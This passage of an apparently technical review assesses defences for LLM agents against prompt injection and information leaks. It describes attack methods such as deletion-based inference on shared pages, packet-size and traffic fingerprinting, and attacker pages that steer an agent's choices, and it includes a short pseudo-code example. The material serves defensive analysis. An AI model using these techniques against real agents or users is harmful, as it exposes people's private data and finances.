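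d₁ =ʟ d₂ ⟹ g(d₁) =ʟ g(d₂)

g is the same on both sides. In the bank balance example, one possible g sends the fixed text "rich!" and another does nothing. Each has the same public effect whatever the balance is, so both satisfy the definition. But the outsider learns about the balance by seeing which of the two happened, and the definition doesn't compare them.

FIDES is stricter in practice than this definition requires, because tool calls inherit the label of the planner model's conversation. A secrecy policy can therefore block a message even if its text doesn't contain the secret. However, Costa and colleagues don't prove that FIDES catches every leak of this kind.

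They object to noninterference because once an agent had called a tool that might read private data, it could no longer call any tool that might have a publicly visible effect. For example, an assistant that had checked the user's calendar could not then look up a train on a public website. They note that TaintDroid, which tracks private data in Android phone apps, and some web browsers made the same compromise.

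The other relaxation in FIDES is an optional exception for answers in a restricted format. If the format allows k options, an answer carries at most log₂ k bits. A developer could use the same reasoning to release private data, for example by allowing a yes-or-no answer about a confidential report to leave the system.

The limit applies to each answer, so the total leak can grow with the number of answers. Releasing 14 yes-or-no answers about a PIN can reveal all of it, just as 14 refusals can. A policy would need to count the bits already released, but the basic policies in FIDES apply only to the latest action. Costa and colleagues say it would be straightforward to extend FIDES with policies that cover the whole history.

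Garby and colleagues show how to build a similar exception in LLMbda. Their function first endorses the value, then releases the endorsed copy only if it is on a fixed list. It has to endorse first because checking the unendorsed value would make the decision depend on untrusted data, and `endorse` has no effect after such a decision. The list has to be fixed in advance, since an attacker who could extend it would get around the limit. Garby and colleagues have not yet formally proved that this function stays within log₂ k bits.

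This approach makes exceptions easier to review because each one is a visible command in the program. A short list works for an email's category, but agents also need many values that can't be listed in advance, such as the account number on a bill from a new supplier.

### Should an agent's designers accept these leaks?

The best argument for accepting these leaks is that blocking them would make agents much less useful. Most people would rather have an assistant that can check their calendar and then search for trains, even if the railway company might infer something from the search. A fixed plan also makes deliberate leaks harder, because an attacker can't write the loop that sends the PIN. They have to find a plan that already has a suitable branch or error, and a way to observe the result.

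Agents often make decisions about private data in places where outsiders can see the results. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) demonstrates an attack that exploits this without prompt injection. The attacker shares a page of true and false statements about someone's private life, then asks the victim's agent to tidy it by deleting whatever doesn't match its records. The agent writes nothing private, but the attacker can tell from its deletions which statements are true.

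As a CaMeL plan, this request might look roughly like this:

```
for entry in shared_page:
    if entry not in private_records:
        delete_entry(entry)
```

The attacker wrote the text of each entry, so ordinary tracking finds nothing secret in the arguments. The secret leaks through the decision whether to delete each entry, which reveals one bit. A page with 20 entries can therefore reveal 20 bits in one run, without errors or retries. Strict tracking would label each deletion as dependent on private data, and a policy could then refuse the deletion if the attacker can see the page.

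Shim and colleagues tested this attack on an agent connected to real Gmail and Notion accounts. A defence that asks a model to look for privacy violations still let 34.7% of the sensitive items leak. The researchers didn't test CaMeL or FIDES. Ordinary software checks FIDES's policies, so they are mistaken in arguing that FIDES would be vulnerable because a language model enforces them.

Their own defence, FlowSeal, reduced the leak to 0% in the same test. Its software intercepts every attempt to write or share something and, when necessary, has a separate model compare the proposed output with the private records, checking for indirect disclosure as well as copied text. Across all their tests, between 0% and 3.3% of sensitive items leaked. The software guarantees that the check takes place, but the result depends on the model's judgement.

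*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) describes another way to use a model to look for implicit flows. Before a sensitive tool call, the system replaces one suspicious source in the agent's history with a neutral placeholder and asks a model whether the agent would still make the call. If not, the source probably influenced the decision, and the system raises an alert. In one example, an email containing a supposed company policy causes the agent to forward a message that it otherwise wouldn't forward.

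This can distinguish an important influence from an irrelevant one, which strict tracking cannot. It would let the assistant search for trains after reading the calendar if the search would have been the same without it. But each check needs an extra model call for every source it tests, and the model's stated confidence is not a measured probability of being right. The check also covers only calls the agent is about to make. In the example with the shop's offers, an overdrawn user's agent makes no call, so nothing is checked, and the shop still learns about the account from the missing visit.

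## Leaks through traffic and visible behaviour

Suppose a user in a café asks an assistant whether a payment they received could count as money laundering. Nobody has attacked the assistant, its policies are correct, and encryption hides the question and the answer. But someone else can still record the size and arrival time of each piece of the reply as it travels over the café's Wi-Fi.

Labels can't prevent this leak because they belong to values inside the agent's program. The policy correctly allows the user to read the answer, but the size of an encrypted packet isn't a value that the program passes to a tool, so it has no label and no policy checks it. Unlike leaks through loops, errors and retries, this one doesn't need a plan with a suitable branch.

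A leak like this is passive because the observer only watches. In an active leak, an attacker also plants content where the agent will read it, and that content leads the agent to reveal information through actions that look ordinary.

### Packet sizes in streamed replies

Many chat services stream their replies, sending each token or small group of tokens as soon as the model has produced it. TLS, the standard encryption for web traffic, hides the text but adds only a roughly constant number of bytes, C, to each piece:

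size(encrypted) = size(original) + C

An observer can therefore work out how long each piece is. In *Whisper Leak*, McDonald and Bar Or (2025), two Microsoft researchers, tested whether the pattern of sizes and times reveals the subject of the user's question. They had a language model write 100 questions about the legality of money laundering and sent each one 100 times to 28 commercial models, along with up to 11,716 unrelated questions. They trained classifiers on most of the recorded traffic and tested them on versions of the money-laundering question left out of the training data.

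They scored each classifier by the area under its precision-recall curve, which measures how well it found the target conversations without raising false alarms. A perfect classifier scores 100%, and guessing scores about 50%. The best classifier for each model scored above 97% in 17 of 28 cases. The lowest score was 71%, for Amazon's Nova Lite.

In real traffic, questions about money laundering are rare. McDonald and Bar Or therefore estimated what would happen if an observer saw 10,000 unrelated conversations for each one on the target topic. Let r be the share of target conversations that the classifier flags, and f the share of unrelated ones that it flags by mistake. The share of flagged conversations that are really about money laundering is then

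precision = r / (r + 10,000 f)

For 17 models, the estimated precision was 100% with the classifier set to catch 20% of the target conversations (r = 0.2). That estimate is less certain than it looks. For four of those models, precision fell to 10.5% at a setting that caught 50%, which is what the formula gives for a single false alarm in about 2,300 unrelated questions. If the test contained only about that many questions, it could not measure much lower false-alarm rates. A classifier with a true rate of one false alarm in 10,000 would probably raise none in such a test, but its precision at r = 0.2 would be 0.2 / 1.2 ≈ 17%.

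McDonald and Bar Or also advise reading these estimates conservatively, but they expect a determined attacker to do better than they did by collecting more training data or watching the same person over several conversations. Even 17% might be enough for a government looking for people to investigate.

### Caches shared between customers

Another customer of the same model service may be able to learn something about what a user has sent without seeing the network traffic. McDonald and Bar Or summarise an attack by Zheng and others on services that save time by reusing work from earlier prompts. The reply comes faster if a new prompt starts the same way as a recent one or, in some services, has a similar meaning. An attacker whose requests run on the same machine can send guesses and time the replies. A fast reply suggests that somebody else recently sent that text.

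The agent's labels don't cover the cache because it belongs to the model provider. The agent has to send its prompt to the model and can't control what the provider stores afterwards. Separate caches for each customer would prevent this leak, but the provider would then have to repeat some computation.

### Recognising an agent by its traffic

Agents produce more distinctive traffic than simple chatbots because they use tools. An agent that generates images, for example, may send a short description, pause, and then send a large burst of data. *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (Zhang, Deng and colleagues, 2025) describes AgentPrint, a system that uses such patterns to work out which agent someone is using. The choice of agent can itself be sensitive, for instance if the agent specialises in diagnosing illnesses.

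They tested it on 50 popular GPTs, customised versions of ChatGPT. They wrote 150 prompts for each, recorded the encrypted traffic, and trained a classifier on the number of packets and bytes sent in each direction over time. The classifier reached an F1 score of 0.87, where 1 means no misses and no false alarms, and fell only to 0.85 when the traffic also included agents outside the 50.

These conditions favoured the observer. The attack requires the observer to notice when a conversation starts and the user to talk to only one agent at a time. The researchers also designed the prompts to trigger each agent's special functions and discarded short text-only conversations. They found agents that mostly reply in plain text harder to tell apart.

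AgentPrint can also combine a person's use of several agents to guess their occupation. For simulated users in jobs where language models are especially useful, the correct category was among its top three guesses 73.9% of the time. Always guessing the three most common categories would have been right about 52% of the time, so the choice of agents revealed something about occupation. But a language model invented these users' working days and chose their agents.

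The test with real people is weaker evidence. Zhang and colleagues asked 49 people which of 55 agents they would use at work, then simulated errors in identifying those agents rather than recording traffic. The correct occupational category was among the first three guesses 69.1% of the time. But 33 of the 49 people were managers, technologists, or clerks and service workers, so always guessing those three categories would have been right 67% of the time.

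### The sites a research agent visits

Some people run a research agent on their own computer to keep their questions private. But the agent still has to read the web, and the user's internet provider can usually see the names of the sites it contacts, though not the individual pages. *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents* (Jeong, Teymoorianfard et al., 2025) found that such agents visit 70 to 140 sites for one question. Few people browse like that, so the agent's visits are easy to tell apart from a person's.

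To reconstruct the questions, the researchers ran agents on public search topics and recorded the sites they visited. They gave GPT-4o five of these lists with the matching questions, then asked it to infer other questions from their sites alone. A second model scored the reconstructions from 0 to 1. On 20 test questions, they scored 0.77 for matching the original's purpose, 0.74 for needing the same kind of source, and 0.52 for being about the same things. An observer would often learn that someone was looking for medical advice, for example, but be less sure about the illness.

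Jeong and colleagues summarise this as recovering over 73% of the "functional and domain knowledge" in users' prompts. That figure is an average similarity, not the share of questions the attacker got right. Part of the score also requires very little data, since GPT-4o still scored 0.35 for purpose and 0.41 for the kind of source when it saw only 2% of the sites.

They also inferred personal traits from a simulated week of browsing by invented users, usually 12 to 14 of 32 traits with high accuracy and at most 19. Health insurance and employment status were among the easiest to infer. The researchers had worked five of each user's traits into the questions, which helped the attacker, but some of the other traits could be inferred too.

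The attack assumes that the user has no virtual private network (VPN) and doesn't encrypt site-name lookups. It doesn't need precise timing, which didn't consistently improve the results.

To cover these visits, a secrecy policy would have to treat the user's question as secret and every visit as a message to outsiders. The question determines which sites the agent visits, so the policy would have to block all of them. FIDES and CaMeL can stop an agent from putting a private document into a web address, but an agent researching a question still has to visit sites related to that question.

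### Pages that make the agent choose

Passive observers can only use whatever traffic the agent produces. An attacker who runs a website can get more precise information by giving the agent a choice.

*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, November 2026) gives the example of an agent researching why flu can be deadlier than Covid-19 for children. The agent follows a link on a medical page to further references, which takes it to the attacker's site. The site offers references on clinical outcomes or biological mechanisms. The agent picks biological mechanisms, and the next page offers narrower subjects. The agent never sends the user's question to the site, but each request shows what it is looking for.

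The researchers call this a behavioural covert channel. With four clearly different options, which carry at most two bits per choice, the attacker inferred the right one 93.8% of the time. The number, order or timing of the agent's requests can also carry information, but less reliably. Using timing, the attacker was right only 58.6% of the time. Several small choices in a row worked better than offering more options at once, which didn't help much because accuracy fell to 50% with 16 options.

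For the main test, Liang and colleagues copied about 42,000 web pages and added the link to 2,600 of them. They ran four agents, including OpenAI's Codex, each with three models. The tasks were 500 questions from the StackExchange forums and 378 turns of conversation by people with known profiles. The attacker did not know the question or the page where the agent had found the link.

On the forum questions, the attack got usable choices 94% of the time. In those cases, it recovered the question's main concepts with an F1 score of 0.89, using about six or seven rounds of choices. In the conversations, it got usable choices 83% of the time and recovered facts about the users with an F1 score of 0.80.

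To test how many concepts could be guessed without any leak, the researchers also replaced the agent's choices with random ones. For Codex running GPT-5.5, this reduced the score on the forum questions from 0.81 to 0.10, counting failed attempts as zero in both cases, so nearly all of the information came from the choices.

The passive methods did much worse in the same setting, especially in conversations. An adapted version of AgentPrint identified the right broad category for 43% of the forum questions and 16% of the conversation turns. Jeong and colleagues' method scored 0.73 on the forum questions and 0.08 on the conversation turns for finding the right group of topics. The adaptation may explain part of the poor performance, but neither method seems to transfer easily to new conditions.

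Liang and colleagues repeated their attack against four defences, including FIDES. None lowered the F1 scores by more than 0.03. With FIDES, the score for forum questions fell from 0.89 to 0.87, and the score for user profiles fell from 0.80 to 0.77. By contrast, an ordinary injection that told the agent to send out private data succeeded only 0.38% of the time, even without these defences. The agents were good at refusing to send private data, but following relevant links is a normal part of their tasks.

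The results don't show how often a real attacker could get a link in front of an agent, because the researchers put theirs on pages they knew the agents would visit early in their tasks. They also didn't test CaMeL. A fixed plan that reads a set number of search results and follows no further links would never reach the attacker's site, but it would also do shallower research.

### Edits that other people can see

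An agent that edits a shared document shows its decisions to everyone who can open it. In the shared-page attack by Shim and colleagues, the agent's deletions reveal which statements are true. The researchers tested this in 105 simulated scenarios, running each three times. When a prompt told the agent to ask for consent before answering requests for information, the attack still revealed 75.6% of the sensitive items. With a simpler consent prompt, it revealed 54.7%. The first prompt's stricter rules applied only if the model recognised the task as a request for information, and tidying a page doesn't look like one. The researchers' defence, FlowSeal, reduced the leak to 2.3%.

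FlowSeal's formal guarantee doesn't cover mistakes by the model that checks each output. The researchers tested how much FlowSeal's protection depends on this model, using a related attack in which the agent has to fill in its part of a shared document. FlowSeal normally leaked 0.5% of the items. When they replaced the model's answer with a fixed "safe", it leaked 24.9%. With a fixed answer of "blocked", it leaked 1.3%, but the agent completed none of its ordinary tasks.

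With the model in place, the agent completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, close to the 75.9% with the best prompt-based defence. FlowSeal added about 37% to the running time. The agent was also too cautious. When the data's owner was willing to consent, it shared the requested items only 32.7% of the time, compared with 61% to 86% with the other defences, mainly because it asked for consent less often.

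FlowSeal probably wouldn't stop the attack by Liang and colleagues, because it checks calls that write or share something, and opening a web page counts as reading. Shim and colleagues explicitly exclude traffic analysis.

### Countermeasures and their costs

The table shows how much several countermeasures reduced the attacker's score. The first three rows are for GPT-4o mini, which was unusually hard to protect.

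| Countermeasure | Attacker's score | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Adding random text to each streamed piece | 97.5% → 92.9% | More data to send |
| Sending five tokens at a time | 98.2% → 94.8% | Text appears less smoothly |
| Adding dummy packets | 98.1% → 93.3% | Two to three times the traffic |
| Researching five decoy questions as well | 0.77 → 0.57 for purpose | Six research tasks instead of one |
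| Using only a tenth of the sites | 0.77 → 0.61 for purpose | Almost no loss in report quality |
| Fetching all links and choosing among local copies | 0.89 → 0.39 for concepts | 4.3 times as many page fetches |

McDonald and Bar Or think that random padding probably removes the practical risk from current techniques, despite the score of 92.9%. Sending five tokens at a time removed most of the risk for the other models they simulated. Their main results predate the protections that OpenAI, xAI, Mistral and Microsoft deployed between August and October 2025. Some other providers declined or never replied.

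Sending packets of equal size at a fixed rate would give stronger protection, but it would waste bandwidth and delay the text. Sending the whole reply at once hides the individual pieces but not the total length or the time it took. McDonald and Bar Or mention research showing that even the total number of tokens can reveal, for example, the target language of a translation.

For research agents, visiting fewer sites seems to offer the best trade-off between privacy and report quality. When the agent used a tenth of the sites, a language model rated its reports 8.54 instead of 8.55. The rating fell to 7.65 only when the agent used 2% of them. Most of the visits seem to have revealed information about the user to observers without improving the reports.

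With a VPN, the café or internet provider sees only an encrypted connection to the VPN company. Jeong and colleagues consider VPNs and anonymity networks the only robust protection against their attack, although the VPN company may then be able to see which sites the agent visits. Neither a VPN nor an anonymity network helps against a website that offers the agent a choice, because the site still receives the choice, just from a different address.

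The last row shows Liang and colleagues' own countermeasure. It fetches everything an outside page links to, whatever the user asks, and the agent then chooses among the stored copies. If the agent needs something else, the system mixes that request with randomly selected ones. The attacker still found 91% of the real concepts in the forum questions, but about 71% of the attacker's inferences were now wrong. Someone who watched the same user for months might be able to separate lasting interests from the random ones, but the experiment did not test this.

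A designer could also limit how many visible choices the agent makes in each task. Six choices among four options reveal at most 12 bits, and two choices reveal at most 4 bits. But the first choices are the most useful to an attacker. Liang and colleagues recovered 54% of the main concepts in the forum questions at the first level of their search and 76% after five levels, so even a strict limit would leave much of the leak. The agent would reveal nothing only if it sent the same requests whatever the user asked. It could do that if it only read a fixed list of news sites, but not if it had to search the web for an answer.

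## What a claim of protection covers

Papers on data-flow defences often summarise their results with a claim like "no successful attacks on AgentDojo". Two systems can both fit this description yet protect different things and have very different drawbacks. The claim's meaning depends on what the benchmark tests, which results the researchers excluded, how they configured the system, and how much work the agent could still do.

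### What AgentDojo contains

AgentDojo simulates four settings, called suites, where an agent uses tools. Each suite has user tasks, such as paying a bill, and attacker goals, such as sending money to the attacker's account. *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (2025) reports that the benchmark has 97 user tasks and 629 security cases. Each security case pairs a user task with an attacker goal from the same suite.

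| Suite | User tasks | Attacker's goals | Cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 |

The 629 cases therefore contain only 27 different goals. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports that the benchmark has since grown to over 900 combinations, so the results in two papers that mention AgentDojo may come from different tests.

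The attacker puts text where outside data would normally be, such as in an email or a file. In the standard attack, the attacker disguises this text as an important message from the user, asking the assistant to do something else before the user's task.

### What counts as a successful attack

After each run, ordinary software checks the simulated suite for changes such as a sent email or a money transfer. This avoids relying on a model to judge the result, but it also means that most false answers can't count as successful attacks. A false summary of an email, for example, leaves the mailbox unchanged.

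The travel suite has an exception, where the software searches for a particular piece of text, so an agent that quotes hotel reviews word for word can trigger the check without obeying an injected instruction. Garby and colleagues explain that this was one of two successful injections recorded in the CaMeL paper's evaluation. In the other, the agent made a payment as instructed by a document, which the CaMeL paper places outside its threat model (the attacks CaMeL is meant to stop). For CaMeL, "no successful attacks" therefore means none of the kind it was designed to prevent.

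FIDES's score of zero also depends on which cases count. Besides attacks that only changed text, Costa and colleagues excluded two other kinds of case. In some, AgentDojo had recorded a success even though the policy had blocked the tool call, which is a scoring error. In others, the policies allowed the action, such as sending a Slack message with no link and nothing confidential in it. The attacker had still made the agent send a message, so not everyone would call this a failed attack. The score therefore means only that no attack broke the policies, which software that enforces them correctly should guarantee anyway.

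AgentDojo doesn't label data as trusted or untrusted, so Costa and colleagues also derived the labels in this test from the benchmark, marking a type of field as untrusted if at least one of its attacks used it. This is a reasonable way to test the mechanism by itself, but it rules out the mistake of trusting a field that an attacker can write to. Developers could make that mistake because they have to label their data without knowing which attacks will come.

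### What the protection costs

Narisetty and colleagues cite the CaMeL paper's main results. CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. It used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens, so running it would cost nearly three times as much.

The size of a reported loss, such as seven percentage points, depends on the baseline. In Costa and colleagues' tests with GPT-4o, switching on the policies lowered FIDES's task completion by 4.5 to 16.2 points, depending on the suite, compared with FIDES without policies. On banking tasks, an ordinary agent without a defence completed 98.8%, FIDES without policies 65.0%, and FIDES with policies 52.5%. Most of the loss came from the agent's difficulty in working with hidden data, before any policy had refused anything. A better model reduced the loss on travel tasks, where FIDES with policies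 completed 41% using GPT-4o and 68% using the reasoning model o1.

Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on the banking suite with its policies off and on. Using GPT-5.2, it completed 66.7% of attempts with policies off and 37.5% with them on. Using MiMo-v2.5, it completed 70.8% with policies off and 37.5% with them on. The banking suite is hard for such policies because several of its tasks require the agent to read a file and act on it. The sample is also small, with 16 tasks run three times each.

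Their agent, Randori, written in LLMbda, completed between 64.6% and 75.0% of tasks with its checks always on. It could do this because its planner model is allowed to use `endorse` to mark chosen untrusted data as trusted before seeing it. Without `endorse`, the rate fell from 75.0% to 62.5% with one model and from 64.6% to 54.2% with another. Randori also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the design.

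### The two attacks that beat Randori

Garby and colleagues ran each of the 144 banking cases three times with each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs. Only two attacks succeeded, both in runs of the same case with GPT-5.2. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment described in it, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with their own payment request.

Refusing to endorse anything from files blocks the attack, but Randori then can't pay honest bills from files either.

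Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs, a rate of 0.15%. That rate would mislead someone who uses an agent to pay bills from files, because an attacker who knew this would choose the attack that succeeded. With GPT-5.2, that attack worked in two of its three runs.

Most of the other cases were easy to resist. In 97 of the 144, the attack needs a tool call that the plan for the user's task would never contain, such as a transfer when the user has asked for a summary of recent transactions. Fixing the plan in advance is generally enough to stop these attacks, without labels or policies. Only the remaining 47 cases really test the rules. Randori resisted all 47 in every run with two of the three models, but the sample is small, and Garby and colleagues calculate that even this perfect score is compatible with a true resistance rate as low as 92.4%.

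CaMeL resisted the same attacks almost equally well with and without its policies. Attacks succeeded in 5 of 622 completed runs with policies off and in none of 588 with policies on. The policies halve the agent's usefulness, but this test may understate the protection they add, because its attacks were not chosen to exploit an agent with a fixed plan and no policies.

### Attackers who adapt

*AgentDojo* (2024) warns that it is very easy to build a weak defence that stops any particular attack, so it presents its benchmark as a framework for adding new attacks rather than a fixed list. Filters and specially trained models stopped nearly all attacks from fixed lists, but stopped fewer once researchers designed attacks with knowledge of how these defences worked.

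Narisetty and colleagues adapted an attack to Progent, which doesn't track where values come from but, like CaMeL and FIDES, enforces its rules outside the agent's model. Progent uses a model to write its list of permitted tool calls, and that model can loosen the list after reading tool results. The attack targeted this weakness by describing the malicious action as a harmless step that the user had already authorised.

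Without a defence, 25.8% of the standard attacks succeeded. Progent reduced this to 4.2%, and the adapted attack succeeded only 2.6% of the time. Narisetty and colleagues suggest that the adapted attack's gentler wording made the agent itself less likely to obey. If so, the wording may explain the lower figure as much as Progent does.

They used one small model, Qwen2.5-7B, both as the agent and to write Progent's rules. They tried only one template for the adapted attack, on eight user tasks from each of three suites. In the workspace suite, no attack succeeded even without a defence, which lowers all three averages. On Slack and banking alone, the averages are about 38.7%, 6.4% and 4.0%. Progent also reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 45.2% to 27.1% and needed about 15 times as many model calls.

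In a later and larger test, *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) used a strong model, Gemini 3.1 Pro, to write an injection and improve it over six rounds based on how many times it succeeded. The attacking model had information about the general types of defence but not about which one it faced. Its injections came to avoid anything that looked like an instruction. In one case it wrote the attacker's account number into a bill as updated payment details, and the agent paid. The PIGuard filter had stopped every standard attack on GPT-4o mini, but 28.0% of the rewritten ones succeeded.

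CaMeL and Progent resisted AutoDojo's attacks much better. The table shows the share of tasks each agent completed when it was not under attack, then the share of attacks that succeeded. CaMeL was tested with its policies on.

| Model | No defence | CaMeL | Progent |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini | 66.7% / 52.4% | 26.3% / 0.0% | 63.2% / 7.7% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 77.2% / 8.7% | 52.6% / 1.8% | 73.7% / 1.5% |
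| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 63.2% / 34.7% | 28.1% / 0.3% | 57.9% / 3.6% |
| DeepSeek v4 Flash | 89.5% / 16.5% | 38.6% / 0.5% | 78.9% / 4.6% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.2% / 1.8% | 40.4% / 0.5% | 63.2% / 0.5% |

Attack success rates against CaMeL were almost the same as with the standard attack, as expected of rules that ignore wording. All the successes were in the travel suite, so the check that searches for text may explain some of them. The last row shows why a claim should include the result without a defence. On Claude Haiku 4.5, the standard attack succeeded only 0.3% of the time with no defence, so almost any defence would have scored close to zero.

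CaMeL loses 25 to 51 percentage points of utility in Ma and colleagues' tests, compared with seven in its own paper. The models are different, and Ma and colleagues left out the workspace suite, which probably suits CaMeL best. Costa and colleagues found that only 5% of workspace tasks require the agent to see some data before it can decide what to do, compared with more than 40% in banking and Slack.

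AutoDojo's attacker could change the wording of an injection, but the attacker's goals came from the benchmark. An attacker who knew that a victim used CaMeL could instead choose a goal that CaMeL doesn't try to prevent, such as falsifying a summary. Most of the attacks in STEER-Bench likewise target what a fixed plan doesn't constrain.

### Tasks that change along the way

An agent can also avoid attacks by failing to do its job. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) argue in *AgentDyn* that AgentDojo hides this problem, because only 6 of its 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan as it works. An agent asked to pay a bill saved in a file, for example, can plan in advance to read the file and send money. By Costa and colleagues' wider definition, about 20 tasks depend on data, but a fixed plan still suits most of the benchmark.

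AgentDyn has 560 attack cases and 60 tasks, all of which need replanning. The tasks average 7.1 steps, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo. They also include helpful instructions from outside sources, such as a checkout page that tells the agent to log in first. A defence that ignores every outside instruction will fail these tasks.

No attack on CaMeL succeeded, but this means little because it completed none of the tasks with any of the four main models. Progent kept the attack success rate below 2%, but it reduced GPT-4o's completion rate from 53.3% to 6.7%. Its best completion rate was 25.0% with Gemini 2.5 Pro, compared with 51.7% without a defence. Li and colleagues found that Progent had trouble choosing the right permissions from a larger set of tools and eventually blocked almost everything useful.

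These results are close to a worst case. Every task was a kind that fixed plans handle badly, and the results don't show how common such tasks are in practice. Li and colleagues also told the agents to finish without asking the user for confirmation, which removes the usual way around a strict policy. Ma and colleagues left CaMeL out of their own AgentDyn tests because it would need extensive policies for each suite.

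ROPE, which doesn't fix the plan in advance, did better on these tasks. With ROPE, GPT-4o mini completed 43.3% of AgentDyn's tasks, compared with 46.7% without a defence, and 2.9% of AutoDojo's attacks succeeded. This suggests that much of CaMeL's loss on changing tasks comes from the fixed plan rather than from tracking data. However, ROPE and AutoDojo have the same lead author, so an independent test would be useful.

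### Details to look for in a claim

The table gives the details behind the claims made for four systems. The details for COBRA, which checks web requests and tool calls, come from Zingrillo and colleagues.

| | CaMeL | FIDES | LLMbda | COBRA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Property guaranteed | The agent keeps to its plan, and tool calls obey the policies. No formal proof | Explicit secrecy (no direct copying of secrets to public places), and tool calls obey the policies | Noninterference, apart from what a run reveals by not finishing. `endorse` can weaken trust but not secrecy | The agent keeps to its plan, and checked requests obey the current branch's restrictions |
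| Attacker's powers | Writes data that tools return, but not the user's request | Changes data from untrusted sources and sees the effects of some tool calls | Chooses all untrusted data | Knows the design, controls outside content and adapts to what the agent visibly does, but can't see the plan |
| Actions checked | Tool calls, but not the answer to the user | Tool calls, but not the answer to the user | Calls to sensitive tools, through checks inside the tools | Web requests and MCP tool calls, but not the meaning of text, other email protocols or direct writes to disk |
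| What the observer can see | Tool calls. Some side channels remain, including retries | Changes to public data. The proof leaves out the order of calls, timing and packet sizes | The final result. The proof leaves out timing and actions along the way | The agent's outside behaviour. No guarantee limits what it reveals |
| Who assigns labels | The developer labels each source, and the interpreter passes the labels on | The developer. In the AgentDojo test, the researchers used the benchmark's own attack targets | The developer of the tools, though the planner model can endorse data | A planner model writes restrictions instead, using site and tool descriptions the user has approved |
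| Policies on in the tests? | On in AutoDojo, both ways in the LLMbda paper's banking test | Both. After review, 21 attacks succeeded with policies off and none with them on | Always on | On, then with each protection off in turn |
| Utility lost | 84% → 77% in its own paper. About 69% → 37.5% on banking when policies were switched on | 16 to 46 points, depending on the suite, compared with an ordinary agent using GPT-4o | No clear loss on banking compared with CaMeL without policies. No comparison with an ordinary agent | 3% on STEER-Bench. 51.0% → 38.8% on desktop tasks with Claude Sonnet 5 |

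With these details added, the claim of "no successful attacks on AgentDojo" would, for FIDES, be that no attack made the agent break its policies when it used GPT-4o and the policies were on. The attackers knew which tools the agent had but didn't adapt to the defence, and the researchers had labelled as untrusted every type of field the attacks used. Without attacks, FIDES completed 41% to 59% of the tasks, depending on the suite, while an ordinary agent completed 70% to 99%.
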